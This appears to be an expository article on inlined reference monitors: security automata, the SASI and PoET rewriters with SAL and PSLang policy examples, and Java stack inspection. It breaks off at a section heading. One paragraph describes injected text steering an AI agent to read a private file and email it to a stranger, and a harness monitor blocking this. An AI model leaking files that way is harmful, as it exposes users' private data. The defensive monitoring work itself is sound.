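# Inlined Reference Monitors and Their Policy Languages, from SASI to Polymer and Agent Harnesses

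## Reference monitors, security automata and the idea of inlining

An inlined reference monitor is a security check that a tool inserts into a program before the program runs, so that the program enforces a policy on itself. The tool is called a rewriter, and the untrusted program is called the target. *SASI Enforcement of Security Policies* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 1999) described the first two prototypes, one for Intel x86 code and one for Java, and other researchers later applied the technique to web pages and Android apps. The technique combines the reference monitor, developed in military computer security in the early 1970s, with the rewriting of machine code, which programmers had used for measurement and memory protection.

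### The reference monitor

A reference monitor checks every security-relevant action before it happens and can stop it. Anderson (1972) set out the concept in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* for the United States Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Existing defences mostly kept outsiders away from the machine and did nothing against a malicious user with a legitimate account who could write and run their own programs. Anderson's panel proposed checking each reference a program makes to data, a device or another program against a table of what its user may do. The table has a row for each subject (a user or program) and a column for each object (such as a file or device), and each cell lists the kinds of access the subject has to the object.

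The mechanism that carries out these checks must meet three requirements. It must be tamper-proof, since a program that can alter the checks can switch them off. The system must always invoke it; any programs that run without the checks become part of the security apparatus and have to meet the same standard. It must also be small enough to analyze and test completely, because otherwise nobody can justify certifying that it works in every case.

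Anderson's example of a failure is GCOS III, the operating system of the HIS 635 computer. The hardware had a bounds register that kept each user's program inside its own area of memory. But programs called on the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran in a mode that suspended the bounds check, so the check was not always in force. The operating system itself did not qualify as a reference monitor either, because it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, too many for anyone to analyse completely, and a number of penetration exercises against it had already succeeded.

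Later writers use somewhat different terms for these requirements. The trusted computing base (TCB) is all the code that must be correct for the policy to hold, and Anderson's size requirement means keeping it small. Operating systems have since moved far from that ideal. Schneider, Morrisett and Harper's *A Language-Based Approach to Security* cites Windows 2000, which has millions of lines of source code and a graphics subsystem largely inside the kernel for speed. Complete mediation means that no security-relevant event occurs without a check. Vanoverberghe and Piessens's *A Caller-Side Inline Reference Monitor for an Object-Oriented Intermediate Language* calls this "non-trivial" to ensure when a rewriter works on modern object-oriented code.

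Transparency, which has no counterpart in Anderson's list, means that a program that already obeys the policy behaves the same after rewriting. It becomes important once the enforcement mechanism edits the program. The thesis *Inlined Reference Monitors Certification, Concurrency and Tree Based Monitoring* lists it alongside security, meaning that the injected code enforces the policy, and conservativity, meaning that the injected code adds no behaviour of its own.

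### Security automata

A monitor needs a policy precise enough to execute. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) specifies such policies with security automata. A security automaton is a state machine that reads a program's actions one by one. It has a set of states, one or more of which are initial, and a transition relation that gives the possible next states for each current state and action. If an action has no possible next state, the policy forbids it, so the automaton rejects the action and the monitor halts the program.

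Let Q be the set of states, Q₀ the set of initial states and I the set of possible actions. The transition function δ: Q × I → 2^Q maps a state and an action to a set of states. The automaton's current set of states, Q′, starts as Q₀. When the automaton reads an action s, it replaces Q′ with the union of δ(q, s) over every q in Q′, and it rejects if that union is empty. In a deterministic automaton, Q′ never contains more than one state.

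A policy that forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file might keep a downloaded program from leaking what it finds on a disk. The automaton for this policy has two states. It starts in *no file read* and moves to *file read* when the program reads a file. Any other action leaves it in *no file read*. In *file read*, every action except a send leaves the state unchanged, and a send has no transition. The table shows two programs that attempt the same three actions in different orders.

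| Step | First program | State afterwards | Second program | State afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Send | *no file read* | FileRead | *file read* |
| 2 | FileRead | *file read* | Compute | *file read* |
| 3 | Compute | *file read* | Send | none: rejected |

The automaton accepts the first sequence because the program sends its message before it reads anything. It rejects the second at step 3, and the monitor halts the program before it sends the message.

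This policy needs only one bit of memory. For larger policies, Schneider replaces the diagram with variables and guarded commands, which are rules that test the current action and the variables and then update the variables. His access-control policy keeps sets of principals, objects and rights, and its rules determine who may use, grant or revoke a right. Drawing the same policy as a flat collection of states would be very awkward.

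The automaton enforces the policy only if *FileRead* and *Send* are defined correctly. A program may have many ways to send a message, some of them "buried deep within the bowels of the target", as Schneider puts it, and the policy's author has to find them all. If the definition of *Send* omits one, the target can leak the file even though the automaton works as designed. The events and values that a policy can refer to are its policy vocabulary, and the difficulty of getting this vocabulary right recurs in every later system.

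### What a monitor can enforce

Schneider's main result is about limits. A monitor that watches one execution and can only halt it enforces nothing but safety properties, which are policies that some bad thing never happens. The argument starts from what such a monitor knows:

- It sees a single execution, so the policy must be a test that each execution passes or fails on its own.
- It cannot see the future, and the target may stop at any moment. It therefore cannot let a violation pass in the hope that later steps will make it good, and once a sequence of actions breaks the policy, every continuation of the sequence must break it too.
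- It has to act at some definite step, so every forbidden execution must have a finite beginning that the policy already forbids.

A policy that meets all these conditions is a safety property. The file-and-message policy is one because any execution that breaks it contains a first send after a read, and nothing the program does afterwards can undo that violation.

Liveness properties require that something good eventually happens, so no finite part of an execution can show that one has been violated. If the policy is that no user waits forever for a resource, access might still come at the next step however long a user has waited, so the monitor never has grounds to halt the target. Schneider also gives a commercial example, in which a monitor can prevent a seller who has taken payment from doing anything except deliver the service. The seller can still do nothing, and halting the seller's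 program would not deliver the service.

Information-flow policies restrict what an observer can infer about secret data, and a single execution is not enough to determine whether a program complies. If a program prints 0 whatever the secret is, the observer learns nothing from the output, but if it prints 0 for only one value of the secret, the observer learns that value. The monitor sees the same action in both cases. To distinguish them, it would need information about what the program would have printed if the secret had been different.

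A monitor can enforce a stricter safety property that rules out the leak along with much else. The ban on sending after reading, for example, blocks any later message, whether it contains the file or only the time of day. Schneider points to the limiting case, a policy that forbids every execution, which is perfectly secure but useless. A policy author who approximates information flow with a safety property has to choose a less strict policy than that.

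A monitor also cannot enforce every safety property. A rule that no user waits more than a fixed number of seconds is a safety property, because any violation occurs at a definite point, but time keeps passing after the monitor halts the target, so halting does not prevent the violation. If the rule counts execution steps instead of seconds, the monitor can enforce it, because a halted program takes no more steps.

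Schneider excludes compilers and theorem provers from the class of mechanisms the result covers, because they examine the program's text and, through it, all the program's possible executions. He also excludes tools that modify the target. An inlined monitor that only simulates a security automaton can't enforce any new kind of policy by running inside the program, but edit automata, which can also suppress and insert actions, can enforce policies beyond safety properties. Halting monitors have the advantage of being simple to combine, since running two in tandem enforces both policies.

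### Moving the monitor into the target

The usual way to make a monitor tamper-proof is to put it in a separate address space, a region of memory that the hardware prevents the target from accessing. Erlingsson and Schneider identify two drawbacks. One is slower execution, because each security-relevant event forces a context switch, in which the processor stops running the target and runs the monitor, and the system must often copy data between address spaces as well. The slowdown is small for file access, since a program that opens a file has to call the operating system anyway, but it could be very large for a policy that concerns every machine instruction.

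The other drawback is a restricted policy vocabulary. A monitor in the operating system gets control when the target makes a system call, so its policies can cover files but not operations that an application performs internally. Schneider and colleagues illustrate this with two email viruses of the period, Melissa and the Love Bug. Each travelled as a script inside a message. The mail program ran the script when the user opened the message, so the kernel had no opportunity to intervene. The script ran with all the user's privileges, so it could read the address book and send copies of itself to the user's friends.

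Inlining addresses both problems by placing the monitor's code in the target program. For the file-and-message policy, a rewriter adds a variable to the program, initially 0. It inserts code that sets the variable to 1 before each instruction that reads a file, and code that checks the variable before each instruction that sends a message and halts the program if it is 1. These additions take a few ordinary instructions instead of a context switch, and the rewriter can attach them to anything it can recognise in the code, down to a single machine instruction. Schneider and colleagues specify an inlined monitor by its security events, its security state (what it stores about earlier events) and its security updates, the pieces of code that run at an event and change the state or block the action.

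Programmers had edited object code for related purposes long before. Erlingsson and Schneider trace the practice to a 1969 measurement tool for the SDS-940, a time-sharing system at Berkeley. *Fay*, a much later paper on tracing distributed software, draws on the same tool for the lesson that machine code checked for safety before it runs is an efficient and extensible basis for tracing.

Software fault isolation is more closely related to inlining. In *Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation*, Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues (1993) wanted to contain faults in distrusted modules without a context switch every time closely connected modules called one another. They loaded each distrusted module into its own portion of the application's address space, a "fault domain", and modified the module's object code so that it could not write or jump outside that domain. The technique is still used. Kolosick,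 Narayan and colleagues count WebAssembly, a format for compiled code that web browsers run, among its toolkits, and Yedidia, in *Lightweight Fault Isolation*, attributes growing demand for the technique to cloud services that must run untrusted code with little delay. Fault isolation enforces one fixed policy about memory. Erlingsson and Schneider generalised it to any policy that a security automaton can express.

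The drawback of inlining is that the target program may be able to tamper with the checks. In the file-and-message example, a target that could reset the added variable to 0 after reading a file could then send any message. Erlingsson and Schneider therefore require that the target never modify the variables the automaton depends on or jump around the inserted code. The target also must not change its own code or cause other code to run, for instance by linking in a library during execution, because that could undo the other protections. A rewriter can enforce these requirements by verifying that the target does none of these things, or by editing the target so that it cannot.

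The rewriter is therefore responsible for meeting Anderson's requirements. It has to find every event and protect every check, and it belongs to the TCB, as does any analysis it relies on. If it works on object code, the compiler that produced the target can be left out of the TCB, provided the rewriter assumes nothing about how that compiler behaves. Anderson's panel would probably have been wary of inlining. It saw little chance of securing an existing operating system by retrofit, partly because nobody could tell whether every part that needed a control had one. Inlining is also a retrofit, but a tool inserts the checks by a uniform rule, so whether they cover every event depends on one program, the rewriter.

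### Agent harnesses and tool calls

AI agents have revived the question of where a reference monitor should sit. An agent harness is the program that runs a language model in a loop and carries out the actions it requests. A tool call is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments, such as one that reads a file at a given path. The Model Context Protocol, an open standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024, defines how a harness finds and calls tools that separate servers provide. No one can inspect an agent's sequence of actions in advance, because the model chooses each call during the run, and text in a file or web page that it has just read can change the choice. An agent that reads a private file and then emails a stranger produces the sequence that the automaton above rejects. The harness receives each call's name and arguments before anything runs, so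 a monitor there can intercept the call and apply a policy written in terms close to the application's. A command-line tool gives the monitor much less detail to check, because the harness receives only the text of the command, and the files and connections that the resulting program opens are visible only at lower levels of the system.

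## Inserting a security automaton into object code: SASI

Erlingsson and Schneider built SASI (Security Automata SFI Implementation) to generalise software fault isolation (SFI). Fault-isolation tools such as the one by Wahbe and colleagues add code only before instructions that access memory or jump. SASI starts by adding code before every instruction to simulate the security automaton. The x86 prototype works on assembly code from the GNU C compiler (gcc), and the Java prototype works on bytecode, the instructions that a Java virtual machine runs. Both use the same policy language.

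### The policy language

SAL, the Security Automaton Language, expresses an automaton's diagram as text. A SAL policy is a finite list of states, each with its transitions to other states. Every transition has a predicate, a test on the next instruction that determines whether the automaton can take it. Predicates combine constants, variables and C-style operators with functions that describe the target. On x86, these functions give the instruction's opcode (the operation it performs), its operands, and the addresses that the target may read, write or jump to. On Java, they also give the names of classes and methods and the types of a method's arguments. SAL allows only deterministic automata, but this doesn't rule out any policies, because every nondeterministic security automaton has a deterministic equivalent.

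Here is the policy that forbids messages after a file read, written for the Java prototype:

```
/* matches a call to one particular method */
MethodCall(name) ::= op=="invokevirtual" && param[1]==name;

/* the two events that matter to this policy */
FileRead() ::= MethodCall("java/io/FileInputStream/read()I");
Send()     ::= MethodCall("java/net/SocketOutputStream/write(I)V");

/* initial state: the target has read nothing yet */
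start ::=
    !FileRead() -> start
    FileRead()  -> hasRead ;

/* the target has read a file, so only non-sends may follow */
hasRead ::=
    !Send() -> hasRead ;
```

The first three definitions are macros, which SASI expands before it uses the policy. `invokevirtual` is the bytecode instruction that calls a method on an object, and the exclamation mark means "not". SAL has no explicit way to forbid an action, so the policy writer leaves out the transition that would allow it. The `hasRead` state, for example, has no transition for a send.

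The example is only an illustration, and its macros match far fewer operations than their names suggest. `FileRead` matches only the method that reads one byte. Java's `FileInputStream` also has methods that read many bytes into an array, and a program that used only those would stay in `start` and could send everything it had read.

### Four phases of rewriting

A complete automaton in front of every instruction would make the target extremely slow, so the rewriter removes most of it before the program runs. It works in four phases:

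1. **Insert.** The rewriter places a copy of the automaton before each instruction in the target.
2. **Evaluate.** At each copy it already knows which instruction comes next, so it works out the value of every predicate that depends only on known information.
3. **Simplify.** It deletes the transitions whose predicates are false.
4. **Compile.** It translates what remains into object code that updates a state variable or, where the automaton has no transition, halts the target.

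The middle phases are a form of partial evaluation, which computes the parts of a program whose inputs are already known and leaves a shorter program for the rest. A later paper, *Program specialization for execution monitoring*, similarly uses standard partial evaluation to perform some of a security automaton's checks while the tool transforms the program.

In the file-and-message policy, an instruction that adds two numbers is neither a file read nor a send. Both states simply lead back to themselves, so the rewriter inserts nothing. Before a file read, both states lead to `hasRead`, so the inserted code can set the state variable without testing it. Only before a send does the code need a test. Erlingsson and Schneider print the resulting bytecode, in which 0 stands for `start` and 1 for `hasRead`:

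```
ldc 1                       ; added: take the number 1
putstatic SASIJVML/state    ; added: make it the current state
invokevirtual java/io/FileInputStream/read()I        ; original file read
...
getstatic SASIJVML/state    ; added: fetch the current state
ifeq SUCCEED                ; added: if it is 0, skip the next line
invokestatic SASIJVML/FAIL()V                        ; added: halt the target
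SUCCEED:
invokevirtual java/net/SocketOutputStream/write(I)V  ; original send
```

The rewriter can evaluate every predicate in this policy before the program runs, because each depends only on which method the instruction names. Other policies depend on values that exist only at run time. Shmatikov's *0x1A Great Papers in Computer Security* gives the example of a ban on division by zero. The rewriter can identify the division instructions and drop the check everywhere else, but it usually has to leave a test of the divisor before each division.

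SASI simplifies each copy of the automaton separately, which leaves some unnecessary checks in place. Erlingsson and Schneider demonstrate this with a policy that requires a routine to push exactly one value onto the stack before it returns. Their example routine has three instructions, which square a number, push the result and return. The rewriter adds nothing before the multiplication. Before the push, it adds code that changes the state from 0 to 1, or aborts if the state is not 0. Before the return, it adds code that aborts if the state is still 0. If the program can reach the return only directly from the push, the state is always 1 there, so the last check is unnecessary.

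To remove that check, the rewriter would have to analyse how control moves through the whole routine. Erlingsson and Schneider decided against this because it would make the trusted computing base larger and more complex. Schneider and colleagues later explained that a mistake in the optimiser could delete a check that the policy needs.

### Protecting the inserted code

To keep the target from overwriting the state variable or jumping past a check, the x86 prototype prepends a second policy, also written in SAL, to whatever policy the user supplies. The added policy has these rules:

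- The target may return from a routine only if the address on top of the stack is a valid return point.
- It may call or jump only to valid destinations.
- It may read and write only at addresses open to it.

SASI therefore uses its own mechanism to protect the monitor. This works because gcc's output does not modify itself, behaves the same if a tool inserts instructions that do nothing, and has all its variables and jump destinations among the labels that gcc identifies during compilation. The rewriter gets its lists of valid addresses from these labels. Restricting jumps to them also prevents jumps into the middle of an instruction. Because x86 instructions vary in length, such a jump can make the processor read the remaining bytes as a different instruction, which the rewriter has never checked.

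Erlingsson and Schneider give an informal proof that this protection is sufficient. Suppose a target subverts the monitor, and let *i* be the first instruction that does so. Only a branch, call, return or write can subvert the monitor, so *i* is one of these, and SASI puts a check immediately before each of them. Nothing earlier has subverted the monitor, so the target must have executed the check before reaching *i*. The check uses accurate information about which addresses are valid, so it would have halted the target. Instruction *i* therefore never ran, which contradicts the assumption that it subverted the monitor.

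The proof assumes that every dangerous write has an accurate check, but the prototype omits some of these checks. Code from gcc usually reaches local variables through the %ebp register, which gcc guarantees will point into the stack. These accesses are so common that checking them all would slow programs considerably, so the prototype relies on gcc's guarantee instead. Erlingsson and Schneider call this "a questionable trade-off" because it makes the compiler part of the trusted computing base. They accepted it to compare SASI fairly with MiSFIT, an existing fault-isolation tool that makes the same assumption.

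Their doubts were justified. In *Evaluating SFI for a CISC Architecture*, McCamant and Morrisett showed that an ordinary C program could move the stack pointer out of the legal data region and then write to memory the policy was supposed to protect. Both SASI and MiSFIT allowed the write because they trusted the compiler to manage the stack. Compilers are large and may contain bugs, and McCamant and Morrisett add that the safety guarantees compilers provide are loosely specified and have exceptions. The proof by first subversion is valid, but one of its premises was false for the prototype.

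The Java prototype needs no extra memory policy because Java bytecode is type-safe, so a program can use each value only in the ways that its type allows. Any program that broke the x86 version's memory rules would also violate type safety. The rewriter gives its own variables names and types that prevent the target from accessing them. Type safety also prevents jumps to unlabelled instructions, and the added code has no labels inside it, so the target cannot jump into the middle of that code. The label `SUCCEED` in the listing marks the original send, and since the rewriter creates this label, none of the target's own jumps go to it.

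Two features of Java could still defeat the monitor. Dynamic class loading lets a program load new code while it runs, after the rewriter has finished. Reflection lets a program look up classes, variables and methods at run time, which could give it indirect access to the monitor's state. Every policy for the Java prototype must therefore forbid both features, so SASI cannot support even harmless programs that depend on them.

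Inserted code might also break a program that already obeys the policy, for instance by changing the distance between two instructions. Erlingsson and Schneider were surprised to find that the inserted code did not affect the correctness of the programs they tried. They credit high-level languages, which discourage programmers from relying on where the compiler places data and code. This is encouraging for transparency, but it is an informal observation about those programs.

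### The cost on x86

Small (1997), in *A Tool for Constructing Safe Extensible C++ Systems*, presented MiSFIT as a way to let users add their own C++ code to an operating system without endangering the rest of it. MiSFIT overwrites the high bits of every address so that the address always falls inside the program's own memory region. A stray write then lands where it cannot harm the host, and the program continues. SASI instead compares the high bits with the permitted value and halts the program if they differ. For one write to an array, MiSFIT replaces the original instruction with six instructions, while SASI keeps the original and puts six more in front of it.

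Erlingsson and Schneider ran three of Small's operating-system benchmarks through both tools, giving SASI no policy except its built-in memory protection. They averaged 30 runs on a 266 MHz Pentium II. The table gives running times as multiples of the unmodified program's time.

| Benchmark | What the program does | MiSFIT | x86 SASI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page-eviction hotlist | Searches a linked list for a memory page to evict | 2.378 | 3.643 |
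| Logical log-structured disk | Simulates a layer of disk-management software | 1.576 | 1.654 |
| MD5 message digest | Computes a checksum of a block of data | 1.331 | 1.363 |

SASI takes about 5% longer than MiSFIT on the disk benchmark and 2% longer on MD5, but 53% longer on the hotlist. Erlingsson and Schneider also mention other programs on which MiSFIT does considerably better, and they expected further optimisation to narrow the difference. Part of the difference probably arises because SASI halts the program on an illegal address, while MiSFIT changes the address. McCamant and Morrisett tried both methods in their own x86 tool, and checking for illegal addresses added 12% on average.

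The comparison with the unmodified programs matters more for a general-purpose monitor. SASI prepends the memory-protection policy to every x86 policy, so these slowdowns of 36% to 264% come before the rewriter adds any checks for the user's own policy. A policy about file reads and messages might need very few checks, but the target would still run all the memory checks that protect them.

Much of this overhead may be avoidable, because SASI's built-in policy checks both reads and writes. Small measured MiSFIT with and without read protection on an older 120 MHz Pentium. The hotlist program showed no slowdown when MiSFIT protected only writes and calls, but took 3.2 times as long when it also protected reads, because the program spends its time scanning a list and writes very little. By the reasoning of the first-subversion proof, a read cannot subvert the monitor, so a version of SASI without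 read checks could still have protected its own state. It would not have kept the host's data secret from the target, which some users need.

### Reimplementing the Java SecurityManager

For the Java prototype, Erlingsson and Schneider reproduced the SecurityManager of Java 1.1, a security mechanism that Java's developers have since withdrawn. Sun, the company that created Java, had written calls to the SecurityManager into the system libraries at fixed points, such as the methods that open files. Each call ran a check function that could refuse the operation. Erlingsson and Schneider wrote a SAL policy of about four pages that inserted checks at the same points in three library packages, `java.lang`, `java.io` and `java.util`. Their checks called the same functions as Sun's, so that the two versions would behave identically.

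Small timing tests found no statistical difference in overhead between the two versions. Both run the same check functions at the same points, so the result shows that a call inserted by a rewriter adds about as much overhead as one that a library's author writes by hand. The tests did not measure the overhead of a policy that has to track a program's history. They also did not include the x86 design's high-overhead memory checks, which are unnecessary here because type safety protects the monitor.

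The main benefit of the SAL version is flexibility. Adding a checkpoint to Sun's design required a new release of Java, whereas a SASI user could edit the policy and rerun the rewriter. The rewriter can also omit checks where it can determine that they will succeed, for example in a component the user trusts, while Sun's libraries call the SecurityManager every time. Erlingsson and Schneider suggest this could make some programs up to four times faster. They base the estimate on benchmark data from Naccio, another Java system of the period, not on a test of SASI.

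### The size of the trusted code

Both prototypes depend on a SAL compiler and a rewriter, which Erlingsson and Schneider wrote in Java. They give these approximate sizes, in lines of code:

| Component | x86 | Java |
|---|---|---|
| SAL lexer and parser (shared) | 1,600 | 1,600 |
| Partial evaluator (shared) | 1,600 | 1,600 |
| SAL compiler | 850 | 1,000 |
| x86 rewriter, including code analysis | 1,100 | – |
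| Bytecode assembler and disassembler | – | 3,950 |
| Total | 5,150 | 8,150 |

A few thousand lines is small enough for a careful person to read, which was one of Anderson's requirements for a reference monitor. The Java total includes an assembler and a disassembler that any Java virtual machine already has to trust, so SASI adds only about 4,200 lines. The Java compiler stays outside the trusted computing base because the virtual machine checks the bytecode's type safety itself. The x86 total is less reassuring because it omits gcc, and the prototype's security depends on gcc handling the stack as expected.

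### Why the prototypes were not practical

Erlingsson and Schneider concluded that neither prototype could become a practical tool, for two reasons that both concern writing policies. One is that a SAL policy can record very little about the target's past, because all of it must fit into the current state, which is one entry in a finite list. Suppose a policy lets a program delete only the files it has created. The monitor must store the files' names, but a SAL state cannot hold a string, and a policy author cannot write a separate state for every possible set of names. Schneider's notation has variables, so the limit comes from SAL and not from security automata in general.

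Erlingsson and Schneider later remedied this by giving policies typed variables in a new policy language, PSLang. Some other Java systems from SASI's time already allowed extra state, because their policies were partly Java code. Programmers didn't have to learn a new language, but the Java compiler became part of the trusted computing base, which SASI's design avoids.

The other problem is that machine instructions are the wrong events for most application policies. x86 code contains very little of what policy writers want to refer to, although a monitor that could check every instruction had at first seemed able to enforce almost anything. It doesn't even represent functions explicitly, so to find function calls, a policy writer has to search for instruction sequences that resemble the compiler's usual way of making a call. In effect, each policy has to include its own disassembler, which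 Erlingsson and Schneider found awkward and error-prone. Shmatikov calls this the "semantic gap" between individual instructions and the files, strings and function calls that policies refer to.

Checking every instruction makes some additional policies possible. A tool that inserts checks only at method calls, as Naccio does, cannot forbid division by zero or restrict the value of a global variable that the program changes directly. But for a policy about email or files, checking every instruction helps little until somebody has worked out which instructions send the email or open the file.

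One solution would be to rewrite the source code, where functions and types are explicit, but for a C++ program this would add the C++ compiler to the trusted computing base. Erlingsson and Schneider preferred object code that describes the program's structure in a form that a small tool can verify. Typed assembly languages could offer something like this for x86, but Java bytecode already names its classes and methods and includes their types, so the two researchers concentrated on Java for their next system, PoET.

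## Policies with typed state: PoET, PSLang and Java stack inspection

After SASI, Erlingsson and Schneider built PoET (Policy Enforcement Toolkit), which rewrites Java bytecode to enforce policies written in PSLang (Policy Specification Language). PSLang policies attach code to events such as the start of a method, and they can declare variables, whereas SAL had only a finite list of states. Erlingsson and Schneider tested the design by reproducing stack inspection, the access-control mechanism that the main Java vendors had recently adopted.

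### Variables and event handlers

As Aktug and Naliuka (2007), in *ConSpec*, describe it, a PSLang policy begins with variable declarations, which make up the security state. A list of security-relevant events follows. Each event has a piece of Java-like code that runs when the event occurs and can update the variables or report a violation. The sketch below expresses the file-and-message policy in this form, with illustrative keywords:

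```
SECURITY STATE {
    boolean hasRead = false;
}

ON EVENT begin method java.io.FileInputStream.read {
    hasRead = true;
}

ON EVENT begin method java.net.SocketOutputStream.write {
    if (hasRead) {
        FAIL("message after file read");
    }
}
```

The SAL version defines two states and lists what the program may do in each, including actions that leave the state unchanged, whereas this version has one variable and code for only the two events relevant to the policy.

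The difference is greater for policies that SAL could not express. For example, a PSLang policy can let a program delete only the files it has created by keeping a collection of file names, adding a name whenever the program creates a file, and checking the collection before each deletion. But a daily limit on text messages would need to distinguish events in the current run from events in earlier runs, and PSLang has no construct for this. Because policies can contain Java-like code, it is also hard to prove what they do.

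As with SAL, the policy's author still has to find all the relevant methods. For example, a Java program can also read a file through the class `RandomAccessFile`, and the sketch would not detect that read.

PSLang simplifies the rewriter's work. SASI had to derive its checks by evaluating a whole automaton at every instruction, whereas PoET can insert the policy's code almost unchanged at the events the policy specifies. In *Policy-Carrying, Policy-Enforcing Digital Objects*, Payette and Lagoze (2000) describe how PoET takes a policy and the target's class files, breaks the bytecode into its parts, merges in the policy's code, performs integrity checks and produces new class files. Its class loader then passes these to the Java virtual machine (JVM). This process requires neither the program's source code nor a Java compiler. Schneider and colleagues note that a user can enforce two policies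 at once by running the target through the rewriter twice, once for each policy.

### How Java stack inspection decides

Java programs often combine code from several sources. Web browsers in the 1990s ran applets, small programs downloaded with a page, in the same virtual machine as their own code. The system libraries therefore had to distinguish an applet's requests from the browser's. Checking only the immediate caller is not enough, because an applet without file access could call a trusted method that reads files on its behalf. Security researchers call this a confused deputy attack, in which a program with more authority misuses it for one with less.

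Stack inspection looks at the whole chain of callers, which the virtual machine records on the call stack, with one frame for each method that has started and not yet returned. When Sun's version loads a class, it assigns the class to a protection domain, a group of classes with the same origin and permissions. Each frame has the permissions of the domain whose code it is running.

Wallach and Felten (1998), in *Understanding Java Stack Inspection*, set out the algorithm that Sun, Netscape and Microsoft shared. Before a library performs a protected operation, it asks for a check of the corresponding permission. The check starts at the newest frame and works back towards the oldest:

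1. If the frame's domain lacks the permission, the check fails and throws an exception.
2. If the frame has the permission and has marked itself as privileged for it, the check succeeds and the walk stops.
3. If the frame has the permission but no such mark, the check moves to the next older frame.

A frame can also disable a privilege, which makes the check fail when it reaches that frame. A trusted method marks its frame as privileged so that the check doesn't depend on its callers' permissions, and the mark disappears when the method returns. An untrusted method gains nothing by marking itself, because the stack walk tests the permissions of the method's domain before it looks for the mark.

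*Stack Inspection* (Fournet and Gordon, 2002) gives examples with two domains. *System* code may use the screen and files, and *Applet* code may use only the screen. In both chains below, an applet causes the trusted method `readFile` to request the file permission.

| Frame, newest first | Applet asks for the system version | Applet asks to display a secret file |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `readFile` (*System*): has the permission, so continue | `readFile` (*System*): has the permission, so continue |
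| 2 | `readVersion` (*System*, privileged): stop and grant | `displayFile` (*System*): has the permission, so continue |
| 3 | Applet: the walk never gets here | Applet: lacks the permission, so deny |

The first request is harmless because `readVersion` always opens the same file, so the applet cannot use the method's privilege to read anything else. `displayFile` opens whatever file its caller names. Its author has not marked the method as privileged, so stack inspection still checks the applet's own permissions.

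Stack inspection has a serious limit, because a method's frame disappears when the method returns. In another of Fournet and Gordon's examples, a trusted method asks an applet's function for a file name and then displays that file. The applet's function returns the name of a secret file. When the check runs, only trusted frames remain on the stack, so the check passes and the trusted method displays the secret file. *Beyond Stack Inspection*, by Pistoia, Banerjee and Naumann, proposes a model that combines access control with information-flow control. Stack inspection also cannot enforce the file-and-message policy, because the method that read the file has normally returned before the program sends anything. PSLang's variables keep their values after a method returns, so a PSLang policy can cover both kinds of rule.

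### Eager and lazy monitors

An inlined monitor can make the same decisions without a walk if it keeps a running set of the permissions in force. Fournet and Gordon describe this method, which they call eager, with two sets. *S* contains the permissions of the code now running, and *D*, a subset of *S*, contains those that a check would grant. At the start, both contain every permission. They change as follows:

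- When the program calls code whose domain has the permissions *R*, the new *S* is *R* and the new *D* is *D* ∩ *R*.
- When code marks itself as privileged for the permissions *R*, the new *D* is *D* ∪ (*R* ∩ *S*).
- When a call returns or a privileged block ends, both sets go back to their earlier values.
- A check for the permission *p* succeeds if *p* is in *D*.

In the version example, *D* shrinks to {screen} when the applet starts. Calling `readVersion` doesn't change *D*, because intersecting a set with a superset leaves it the same. `readVersion` then marks itself as privileged for files, and since its own domain has that permission, *D* becomes {screen, file}. The call to `readFile` leaves *D* unchanged, so the check succeeds. In the other chain no method marks itself as privileged, so *D* is still {screen} when `readFile` checks for the file permission, and the check fails. Fournet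 and Gordon show that tracking *D* this way always gives the same answer as the lazy approach, which works out the permissions from the stack at the time of the check.

Wallach and Felten had earlier proposed an eager implementation, which they called security-passing style. A rewriter adds an argument to every method, which the caller uses to pass the current security state. The state needs only a finite number of values, because a system has a finite number of domains and permissions. But the monitor must also restore the caller's state after every call, however deeply nested, which requires a stack and so could not be done with SAL's single finite state. Security-passing style uses the program's own stack, since each method still has its own argument when its callees return.

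The two methods do their work at different times:

| Moment | Eager monitor | Lazy monitor |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary call | Works out and passes on the new permissions | Nothing |
| Start of a privileged block | Adds permissions to the current set | Marks the frame |
| Return | Goes back to the caller's set | Nothing, since the frame disappears |
| Check | Looks up one permission | Walks the stack until it reaches a decision |

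In Sun's and Microsoft's versions of stack inspection, a new thread, which has its own call stack, begins with the security state of the code that created it. So a lazy monitor has to save that state when a program starts a thread. Otherwise, an applet could remove its own frame from the record by having trusted code run in a new thread.

The lazy monitor usually does less work because programs call methods far more often than they open files or network connections. Suppose a program makes a million calls and ten checks, with 50 calls in progress at each check. The eager monitor updates its state a million times to make ten quick lookups, while the lazy monitor examines at most 500 frames. The eager monitor would do better in a program that made many checks deep in a chain of calls. Fournet and Gordon observe that lazy evaluation appears to lead to more efficient implementations, and most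 runtimes use it.

Another advantage of security-passing style is that the rewritten program is ordinary bytecode, which runs on any JVM, even one with no support for stack inspection. Compilers can also optimise it more freely. When checks read the real stack, a compiler cannot simply merge a small method into its caller or discard a frame before a method's final call, because either change could affect the result of a later check. With an explicit argument, both optimisations are safe, and the compiler can remove security tracking that no check uses.

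These gains did not make up for the extra work in the system that Wallach, Andrew Appel and Felten (2000) later built. In *SAFKASI*, they rewrote bytecode into security-passing style and combined static analysis with run-time optimisations. They describe the prototype's performance as reasonable but report that traditional stack inspection was still faster.

### Stack inspection as a replaceable policy

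*IRM Enforcement of Java Stack Inspection* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 2000) presents an inlined monitor for each formulation. One updates the security context as the program makes calls, and the other, the lazy version, reconstructs it when a check needs it. The paper evaluates the performance of both, and its abstract reports that one is competitive with the less flexible implementation inside the JVM. That one is probably the lazy version, judging by the relative numbers of calls and checks and by SAFKASI's result.

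The experiment showed that a policy can express a mechanism that vendors had built into the platform, and that at least one way of implementing it need not be much slower than the built-in version. As with SASI's version of the SecurityManager, users can then change the rules themselves. For example, when the walk reached the end of the stack without a decision, Netscape's version denied access, while Sun's and Microsoft's allowed it. PoET's users could choose either rule, or try stricter ones such as Fournet and Gordon's variants, which handle some of the cases that ordinary stack inspection misses.

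The experiment was an easier test of policy writing than a new application would have been. Java's designers had already decided which operations were dangerous and which permission each one required, so the policy only had to reproduce their decisions. Someone writing a policy for an email program would have to make those decisions first. Reproducing stack inspection also did not make it safer, since a faithful copy still lets an applet influence trusted code through the values the applet returns. The performance result covers one policy, whose checks are rare compared with method calls, so it provides little evidence about the overhead of a policy that must respond to very frequent events.

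### Digital objects that carry their own policies

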